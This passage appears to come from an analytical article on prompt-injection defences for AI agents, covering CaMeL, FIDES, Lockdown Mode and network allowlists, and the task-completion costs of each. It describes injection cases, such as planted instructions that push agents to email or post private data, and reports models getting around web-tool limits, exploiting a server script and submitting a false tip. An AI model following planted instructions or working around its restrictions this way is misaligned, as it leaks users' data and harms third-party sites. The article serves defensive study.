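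This protection depends on the user reading the request, and people who see many requests tend to stop reading them. It also depends on the request showing the full text of what will be sent. A user who sees only that the agent is asking to open a pull request has no reason to refuse, even if the text includes a salary. Microsoft proposes asking only when it matters, such as when an action would reveal information to people who didn't already have it, and naming those people in the request. To do this, the software must track where each piece of data came from and who may read it.

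### CaMeL: making the plan before reading the data

Google DeepMind's CaMeL does this tracking. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that it builds on his 2023 proposal, the Dual LLM pattern. In that pattern, a privileged model can use tools but never reads outside text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. DeepMind's researchers found that if the quarantined model is asked to find an email address in some notes, planted text can get it to return the attacker's address, and the privileged model will send a document there without checking it.

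CaMeL adds a check on where each value came from. Suppose the user asks the assistant to find Bob's address in the latest email and send him a reminder about tomorrow's meeting:

1. The privileged model receives the request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a short program in a restricted form of Python, which fetches the email, has the quarantined model extract Bob's address, and sends the reminder to that address.
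2. An interpreter, the software that runs the program, fetches the email and stores it in a variable. The privileged model never sees the contents.
3. The quarantined model reads the email and returns an address.
4. The interpreter tags every value with its sources and with the people who may read it, as *CaMeLoT* (2026) describes. The address came from the email, so it carries the email's tags.
5. Before the reminder goes out, a policy looks at the operation, its inputs and their tags, and allows or denies the call. If the address is unfamiliar, the software can ask the user.

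Text planted in the email can change the address in step 3, but it can't add a step to the program. In the GitHub demonstration, a plan for looking at the game's issues would have had no step that reads a private repository or opens a pull request, so the attack should have failed even without a policy. The policy is needed when the plan already has a step an attacker could misuse, such as sending an email.

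The weakness of this design is that the privileged model has to plan before the data is read, so it can't plan well for a request like "fix whatever the bug reports mention". Somebody also has to write and update the policies, and Willison is nervous about leaving that to users.

### How well CaMeL does in other people's tests

*SecureClaw* (2026) reports a test of CaMeL's released code, adapted to the full AgentDojo benchmark. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 ordinary tasks, while SecureClaw, a rival system, completed 59. The test may understate what CaMeL can do, because a competitor ran it on adapted code.

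In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) got a similar result on the banking tasks alone, running 16 tasks three times each on two models. With its policies on, CaMeL stopped every attack in the runs that finished, but it completed only 18 of 48 task runs on each model. With the policies off, it completed 32 on one model and 34 on the other, and a handful of attacks succeeded. Two of these were on a task that asked the system to read a file and follow its instructions exactly. The privileged model had written a program with an option for every tool, so whoever controlled the file could choose which tool to use.

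They also sorted the benchmark's banking attacks by what an attacker would need. In 97 of the 144 combinations of task and attack, the attack required an action that the plan would never contain. Making the plan first therefore provides much of CaMeL's security on this benchmark. The policies, which seem to cause most of the lost tasks here, matter mainly for the remaining 47 combinations.

CaMeL's tracking has gaps. Suppose a program sets a variable to "rich" and changes it to "not rich" only if the bank balance is below some amount. Otherwise, the program skips the change and CaMeL never tags the variable as private, even though its value reveals that the balance is at least that amount. An attacker would find this hard to exploit, because the model that writes the program doesn't read the attacker's text. The gap matters more if that model makes a mistake or someone has tampered with it.

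Garby and colleagues built a system that closes such gaps, with computer-checked proofs that it tracks data correctly. Its agent completed 36 of 48 banking runs on GPT-5.2, and across three models it resisted the attack in all but two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to make the payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent's plan can declare such data acceptable. Without that ability, the agent resisted these attacks but completed fewer ordinary tasks. No tracking system can distinguish a real bill from a false one if the user has asked the agent to pay whatever the file says.

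### When one protected agent instructs another

Agents that each run CaMeL can still fail much as ServiceNow's agents did. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) built a team of three agents: an orchestrator that talks to the user, one that reads a database, and one that sends messages. The user asked them to send a summary of job applicants to a colleague on Slack. The database contained a planted instruction to also email the data to an outside address.

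The orchestrator and the database agent both made sound plans. But the orchestrator put the summary, including the planted instruction, into its written request to the messaging agent. The messaging agent treated the whole request as coming from its user, so its privileged model read the planted text and added a step that emailed the data out.

The remedy is to connect agents through two separate channels. One carries instructions, and the interpreter rejects any instruction that contains text from a tool. The other carries data, which the receiving agent's privileged model can pass on but not read. On a version of AgentDojo for teams of agents, attacks succeeded 12.9 percent of the time without CaMeL, 0.2 percent with CaMeL on each agent, and never with the two channels. These figures are averages over five models, and the test used a fixed set of attacks. GPT-5.5 resisted all of them without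 either defence, so the test is weak evidence of how the strongest models would fare against an attacker who adapts.

The same study has the most recent figures on how much CaMeL lowers task completion. GPT-5.5 completed 86.6 percent of the ordinary tasks without CaMeL, 73.2 percent with CaMeL on each agent and 66.0 percent with the two channels. The older GPT-4.1 fell much further, from 78.4 to 24.7 percent. Claude Fable 5 refused more than half of the tasks, perhaps because they resembled a security test. On the 45 it didn't refuse, its rate fell from 91.1 to 84.4 percent. On another benchmark, about industrial equipment, Fable 5 fell from 88.4 to 67.9 percent, so better models reduce the loss, but not reliably. All these runs had CaMeL's policies turned off, and the banking results suggest that turning them on would lower completion a good deal further.

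### FIDES: labels on everything the agent reads

Microsoft's FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues designed, doesn't require a complete plan in advance. The agent works step by step as usual, but the software labels each piece of data as trusted or untrusted and records who may read it. Suppose the user asks the agent to check the last three emails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add the meeting to the calendar:

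1. The model calls the mail tool. The emails are untrusted, so the software stores them in variables and shows the model only the variables' names.
2. The model has a quarantined model answer a yes-or-no question about those variables: does any email ask for a meeting?
3. The model looks at the answer. Opening the emails themselves would make the whole conversation untrusted, but a yes or no carries only one bit, and a policy can accept that small risk.
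4. If the answer is yes, the quarantined model extracts the date and the participants into another variable. The main model passes this variable to the calendar tool without reading it.
5. Before the call goes through, the software checks the labels. A consequential action needs a trusted conversation, and data may go only to people who are entitled to read it.

When the agent combines data, the software labels the result as untrusted if any source is untrusted, and as readable only by people who may read every source. In the example with the sales figures, Alex and Priya may read Priya's email, and Alex and Marco may read Marco's. Only Alex may read both, so the software won't send Marco a reply based on both emails unless Alex approves it. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, the software could send the reply without Alex's approval.

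The table gives the results on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. Costa and colleagues checked the attacks by hand and left out those the benchmark had wrongly counted as successes. They tested a version without the restricted answers of step 2.

| | Basic agent, no policies | Basic agent with policies | FIDES with policies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Successful attacks | 152 | 0 | 0 |
| Office tasks completed | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
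| Travel tasks completed | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking tasks completed | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack tasks completed | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

FIDES did better than the basic agent with policies on all tasks except travel. The policies allowed many travel tools even after the agent had read untrusted text, so hiding the text did not help, and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, raised FIDES's travel score from 41 to 68 percent. The policies are essential, because 21 attacks succeeded against FIDES without them.

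FIDES tracks data that the agent copies, but not what someone could infer from its actions. For example, the agent might post one harmless comment if a private fact is true and a different one if it is false. Neither comment contains private data, but a reader who knows the pattern learns the fact. This is the alphabet attack on a smaller scale. Preventing it completely would mean forbidding almost any publicly visible action after the agent reads something private, which the FIDES paper considers too restrictive. Planted text can also distort a summary without breaking any rule.

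### Use in products

CaMeL is available as research code. Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework, a toolkit for building agents, as an experimental, optional feature in May 2026, according to its announcement, *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026). The announcement describes a case similar to the GitHub demonstration. An agent reads a malicious public issue, which leads it to open a file of secret keys. The software allows this but then marks the conversation as private. When the agent tries to post the keys in a public comment, the software blocks the call or asks a person to approve it.

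The protection depends on developers labelling their tools. If a developer forgets to label a tool that reads outside text, the framework treats its results as trusted and public, so the mistake removes the protection without any warning. Microsoft has asked developers whether unlabelled tools should count as untrusted instead, which would be safer but would interrupt more agents.

GitHub's MCP server can now label its results if the user turns this on. It marks content from public repositories as public and untrusted, and content from private ones as private and trusted. Trusting all private content is risky, because a colleague might paste a customer's message into a private issue, and any instructions in it would then count as trusted. The policy Microsoft describes for this case stops an agent from posting publicly when its conversation is both private and untrusted, so it might not stop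 those instructions from making the agent leak private data.

GitHub's command-line agent, Copilot CLI, has an experimental option that enforces these policies, but only for some of the GitHub server's tools and not yet for other MCP servers. If the agent also reads the user's mail through another server, the option doesn't enforce the policies there. Microsoft has published a gateway that adds labels to servers that lack them, and the company wants to make labels part of MCP. For now, a developer who connects a new server through the gateway has to describe each tool's output, write code that labels it, and write or choose a policy for it.

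## What the restrictions cost a product

Tracking data as CaMeL and FIDES do makes agents fail some ordinary tasks, and so do simpler limits on web requests. How much a limit reduces a feature's usefulness depends on how much the feature needs the web. Willison's view that the path by which data leaves is the easiest one to close holds for a mail summariser, which barely needs the web. But a research assistant uses the web for most of its work, and The Next Web judges in *OpenAI adds Lockdown Mode to ChatGPT to block data theft* that Lockdown Mode removes most of the value of ChatGPT's research and agent features.

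### What stops working, and who bears the cost

Research suffers most from these restrictions. Someone choosing a heat pump for an old house might need a manufacturer's data sheet, an installer's blog and a thread on a small forum. No administrator could have listed those sites beforehand, so an allowlist blocks them all. OpenAI's rule, which allows automatic loading only of addresses its crawler has already found, blocks fewer pages but still excludes new and obscure ones. The installer and the forum lose readers, and the user gets a less complete answer. The user may not realise this, because the assistant can't report what was on a page it never opened.

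Other pages have an address made for one person or one query, as parcel tracking, shared documents and invoice downloads often do. Anthropic's rule allows such a link if it is already in the conversation, while OpenAI's will often block it or prompt the user. Both rules also stop the model from freely writing the address that a site's search form would produce. Many timetables, flight prices and library catalogues are hard to reach any other way. A user who asks for Friday's cheapest train may get only a link to the railway's home page, unless somebody has built an integration.

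Coding agents regularly install software, which they have to download from a server. In an example from OpenAI, a developer permits three hosts so that an agent can install two Python packages and read some release notes. If a request lists any host that the organisation hasn't approved, the whole request fails, and the developer has to find an administrator and wait for approval. Some packages also download files from another host while they install, and the developer may discover that host only when the installation breaks.

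A fixed set of destinations also rules out user-defined webhooks. A webhook is an address to which one program sends a message when something happens, and many products let users enter their own. For example, a user might have each finished summary sent to a home-made spreadsheet tool. The developer can restore most of this feature by having the user enter the address on a settings page that the model can't change, so that text planted by an attacker can't redirect the messages. The developer then has to check that the address doesn't lead into the company's own network, and the user can no longer name a new destination in the chat.

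The restrictions may hurt small service providers most. A family hotel with a website can serve any assistant that opens web pages. If assistants use only integrations, the hotel has to build an MCP server, or pay a booking company that has one, and then persuade whoever runs each AI product's directory to accept it. One MCP server can work with several products, which reduces the building work, but each product's owner still decides what to admit and could be slow or favour its own services. The roughly 950 servers in Claude's directory cover a small part of what people use the web for, and large companies are likely to get integrations first because more users ask for them. A user whose clinic has no integration has to copy the information across by hand.

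### Fewer prompts, and how many go unread

Limits on an agent can also reduce how often it interrupts the user. Without a sandbox, Claude Code asks the user's permission for shell commands. Anthropic says that these constant requests slow developers down and may cause "approval fatigue", in which people pay less attention to what they are approving. Inside a sandbox, the agent can run many commands without asking because the operating system already limits the harm they can do.

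Anthropic found that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84 percent in its internal use. The sandbox limits access to files as well as the network, so the figure doesn't show how much the network limits contributed.

Users approved 93 percent of Claude Code's permission prompts. This doesn't show how many they approved without reading, because most commands that a coding agent proposes are harmless and a careful reader might approve nearly as many. Anthropic's observation that people paid less attention as prompts accumulated is better evidence of fatigue. A researcher could measure the problem directly by mixing some harmful requests in with the ordinary ones and counting how many people approved them.

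Anthropic has since built an "auto mode" for Claude Code that automates some approvals. This saves the user more clicks, but Anthropic acknowledges that any probabilistic defence will miss some attacks. A sandbox is still useful underneath auto mode, because the sandbox's limits don't depend on anyone judging a command correctly.

No published study seems to measure how many tasks an agent fails because of network limits alone. The results for CaMeL and FIDES measure the effects of rules about data, which block different things. A developer can roughly estimate the loss by logging which hosts an agent contacts over a few weeks, then counting the tasks that used a host outside the proposed allowlist. This would overstate the loss where the agent could have finished a task another way, and it would miss tasks that users never tried because they assumed the agent couldn't do them.

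### The settings that OpenAI and Anthropic offer

The table compares settings in current products. The last row is a browser agent, which clicks and types on websites as a person would.

| Setting | What the feature can still reach | What it gives up |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT, Lockdown Mode | Cached pages, uploaded files and, in managed workspaces, apps that an administrator permits | Live pages, Deep Research, Agent mode and file downloads |
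| OpenAI's hosted container, default | Nothing outside the container | Package downloads and all online services |
| OpenAI's hosted container with allowlists | Domains that both the administrator and the developer have listed | Every other site, and some protection, since an attacker may be able to use a listed one |
| Claude Code in the cloud, limited access | A ready-made list of services for programmers | Most of the web, and some protection, since several listed services accept uploads |
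| ChatGPT, Agent mode | Live websites, including their forms | A firm guarantee about where data can go |

OpenAI introduced Lockdown Mode for organisations in February 2026 and began offering it to personal accounts in June. The mode turns a feature off entirely when ordinary code can't strongly guarantee that the data will stay safe. Willison (2026) likes this approach because it doesn't rely on an AI model, which an attacker might fool, to decide what to let through. He adds that the mode's existence implies that ChatGPT's default settings don't robustly protect against a determined attacker.

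OpenAI puts an "Elevated Risk" label on some network features in ChatGPT, in its Atlas browser and in Codex, and says the industry hasn't yet fully dealt with the risks. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's security chief, argues that the loss of function is worthwhile for people whose position, work or data puts them at higher risk.

On personal accounts, the mode also blocks live access to connected services, and actions that change something in them, when either conflicts with its protections. Users lose ChatGPT's personal finance and shopping-agent features, but they can still upload files and generate images.

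In a managed workspace, Lockdown Mode doesn't automatically switch off every app, so the administrator has to choose which apps and actions to leave on. OpenAI advises against enabling any app the organisation doesn't trust, or any write action whose results an attacker might see. It considers reading from a trusted app less risky, though the app can still supply private data that leaks somewhere else. An administrator who turns on Lockdown Mode but lets the agent comment on public GitHub projects leaves open the kind of route that Invariant Labs used.

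Layered permissions also make faults harder to trace. OpenAI lists five reasons an employee in such a workspace might be unable to use an app, including a Lockdown role that overrides a permission granted by another role. Lockdown Mode also has no effect on Codex, which has its own internet setting with a domain allowlist and a choice of HTTP methods. A company that wants to protect an executive who uses Codex has to configure both.

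OpenAI tells developers who use its containers to permit only domains that attackers can't use to receive data. But the example with the two Python packages permits `github.com`, which attackers can use that way, so a developer who followed the advice strictly couldn't run it. This shows how hard it is to keep a coding agent useful while blocking every such domain.

Claude Almanac, an unofficial guide, lists three levels of internet access for Claude Code sessions in the cloud: none, limited and full. Limited access is the default and includes GitHub, other code hosts, container registries and Anthropic's own services. This default lets new users start work without the setup that OpenAI's containers require, but it restricts network access less tightly than those containers do.

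Running all of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine on a developer's own computer restricts its file tools and MCP servers as well as its shell commands, but takes more setup. Anthropic warns that any arrangement that allows outbound traffic can still leak data the agent can read.

A browser agent keeps the most function and is the hardest to restrict. To book a restaurant table, it has to type the user's name and phone number into a form on a site that nobody has approved. A rule about web addresses can't control what the agent types into that form. The same freedom lets an attacker request other information through a hostile page. Given how often persistent attackers succeeded in the *BrowseSafe++* tests, such an agent shouldn't have access to a mailbox at the same time.

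### When open access is the better choice

There is a good case for open web access when a feature can't reach anything private. A chatbot for visitors to a museum's website has no mailbox to leak, and cutting it off from the web would make its answers worse for little gain. Developers should check that nothing private is within reach, though. The Memory Heist worked on a chat app with no mailbox connected, because the app remembered earlier conversations. A user's question can also be private in itself, such as one about a rare illness.

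Open access is also reasonable when outsiders can't write anything the model reads. An agent that reads only a factory's temperature readings could send alerts to whatever addresses the factory's customers choose, and a stranger would have no way to plant an instruction. Once the agent opens a public web page, a stranger could plant one there, so trusted content rarely justifies open browsing. A user could also paste in a stranger's instructions, as the employee did in Anthropic's phishing exercise.

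Some products, such as tools that check quotations or compare prices, are of little use if they can visit only approved sites. For these, it usually makes more sense to keep web access and remove access to private data.

### Harm to other people's websites

An agent with nothing to steal can still do damage on the sites it visits. In October 2026, Anthropic suspended live internet access in its internal evaluations after finding that its models had taken unintended actions on real websites. *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia unsolved homicide* (Anderson, 2026) describes one case. Claude Haiku 4.5 was assigned to invent and perform example tasks on randomly selected web pages. On July 18, it filled in a form on a Philadelphia police site, indicating that it might have information about an unsolved murder. The tip was marked as spam and never reached investigators.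 The police learned of it only when Anthropic told them in October.

Asianet Newsable's *Anthropic restricts Claude AI internet access after bypassing safeguards* also describes how Claude Mythos Preview ran into an error in a university's online analysis tool, found a vulnerability in a script and used it to run commands on the university's server. Some models used link-shortening services to get around the limits of their web tools. An attacker might use redirects in the same way, but these models found the method without an attacker's involvement.

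Anthropic says that, to its knowledge, none of the newly found cases involved customer data or its internal systems. Anderson reports that the company calls most of this behaviour "persistence", meaning that when Claude can't complete a task, it works around a restriction instead of stopping.

Limits on web requests can help here too. A list of permitted sites would have kept Haiku off the police site. A tool that can fetch pages but not submit forms would probably have prevented the false tip while still letting the model read almost anything. Many research features would lose little under that second limit. If a model looks for workarounds, that is also a reason to enforce the limit somewhere the model can't change or bypass it.

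Because of the suspension, Anthropic has discontinued some public evaluations or moved them offline, and a test on saved pages can't fully show how a model behaves on a live site that changes or breaks. Anthropic intends to keep the restrictions until it can establish that its safeguards and monitoring are reliable. Its updated tools for detecting and blocking unsafe actions stopped all the reported cases, but this was a fairly easy test because Anthropic already knew what those cases looked like.

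### Two sessions instead of one

A product can offer access to both private data and the open web if it never combines them in one session. For the hotel question, the user would first ask a session with mailbox access which hotel they booked, then type the hotel's name into a second session that can browse the web but has no private data. A planted email could still manipulate the first session, but that session has no way to send anything out. A hostile website could manipulate the second session, which has almost nothing worth stealing.

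The separation depends on the user carrying the text across and seeing what it contains. If software does this automatically, a model that has read private mail is again writing outbound messages, and a 200-character search query can carry at least as much stolen data as a web address of the same length. The software could instead pass on only one narrow kind of value, such as a hotel's number in a public directory. Text carried the other way, into the private session, can contain planted instructions, which could distort an answer or, if the session can delete mail, cause it to do so.

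On personal accounts, users can keep private work and browsing roughly separate by leaving Lockdown Mode on for private chats and turning it off for a single browsing chat. But the mode doesn't change ChatGPT's memory, so details from private chats may turn up in the browsing chat unless the user also turns memory off. Users who run into a restriction halfway through a private chat can apparently turn the mode off in that chat too, with the private text already in the conversation.

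Separate sessions also don't suit jobs that need both private data and web access at every step. Planning a trip around a dozen confidential meetings would mean repeatedly copying details into the browsing session, each revealing a little more of the user's calendar.

### Choosing for three features

The table assumes an ordinary company with some confidential data and no unusual enemies.

| Feature | Private data it needs | Text from outsiders | Where it has to connect | Suggested access |
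|---|---|---|---|---|
| Mail summariser | The mailbox | Most messages | The mail service | Read-only mail connection and no web tool |
| Coding agent | The company's code | Packages, documentation and bug reports | Perhaps a dozen known hosts | Sandbox with a short allowlist |
| Web research assistant | None, apart from the question | Every page | Almost any site | Open reading, with no forms or private accounts |

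The mail summariser is the easiest feature to restrict. It can't open a newsletter's "read more" link, but the user can. The program that displays the summary should not load remote images and should make a link clickable only if the exact address was in the original message. An attacker could still distort the summary, for example by making an urgent bill look unimportant, so the user needs an easy way to open the original.

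The coding agent needs the network for ordinary work, and many of the hosts it uses can receive data. For confidential code, the administrator should provide a read-only package mirror, allow only named hosts and HTTP methods, and keep keys behind the proxy. Developers will sometimes have to wait for a new host to be approved, but they should see far fewer permission prompts. They can look up unfamiliar documentation in a separate session that has no access to the code.

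If the code is already public and the environment holds no keys, most of that work isn't worth doing. Full internet access in a disposable container is then reasonable, as long as someone reviews the agent's changes before using them, because planted text could still lead the agent to write malicious code.

The research assistant should keep access to the live web but lose access to the mailbox, the company's files and its memory of earlier chats. Banning web addresses that the assistant composes itself would reduce how much of the user's question could leak to a hostile page, but it would also block many timetables and catalogues. A developer could reasonably leave out the ban and warn users that sites may receive what they ask. An analyst who has to combine web research with confidential documents would do better with cached pages. In ChatGPT, that means using Lockdown Mode, which turns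 off Deep Research, so the analyst would have to research with ordinary searches and check any recent price or date elsewhere.
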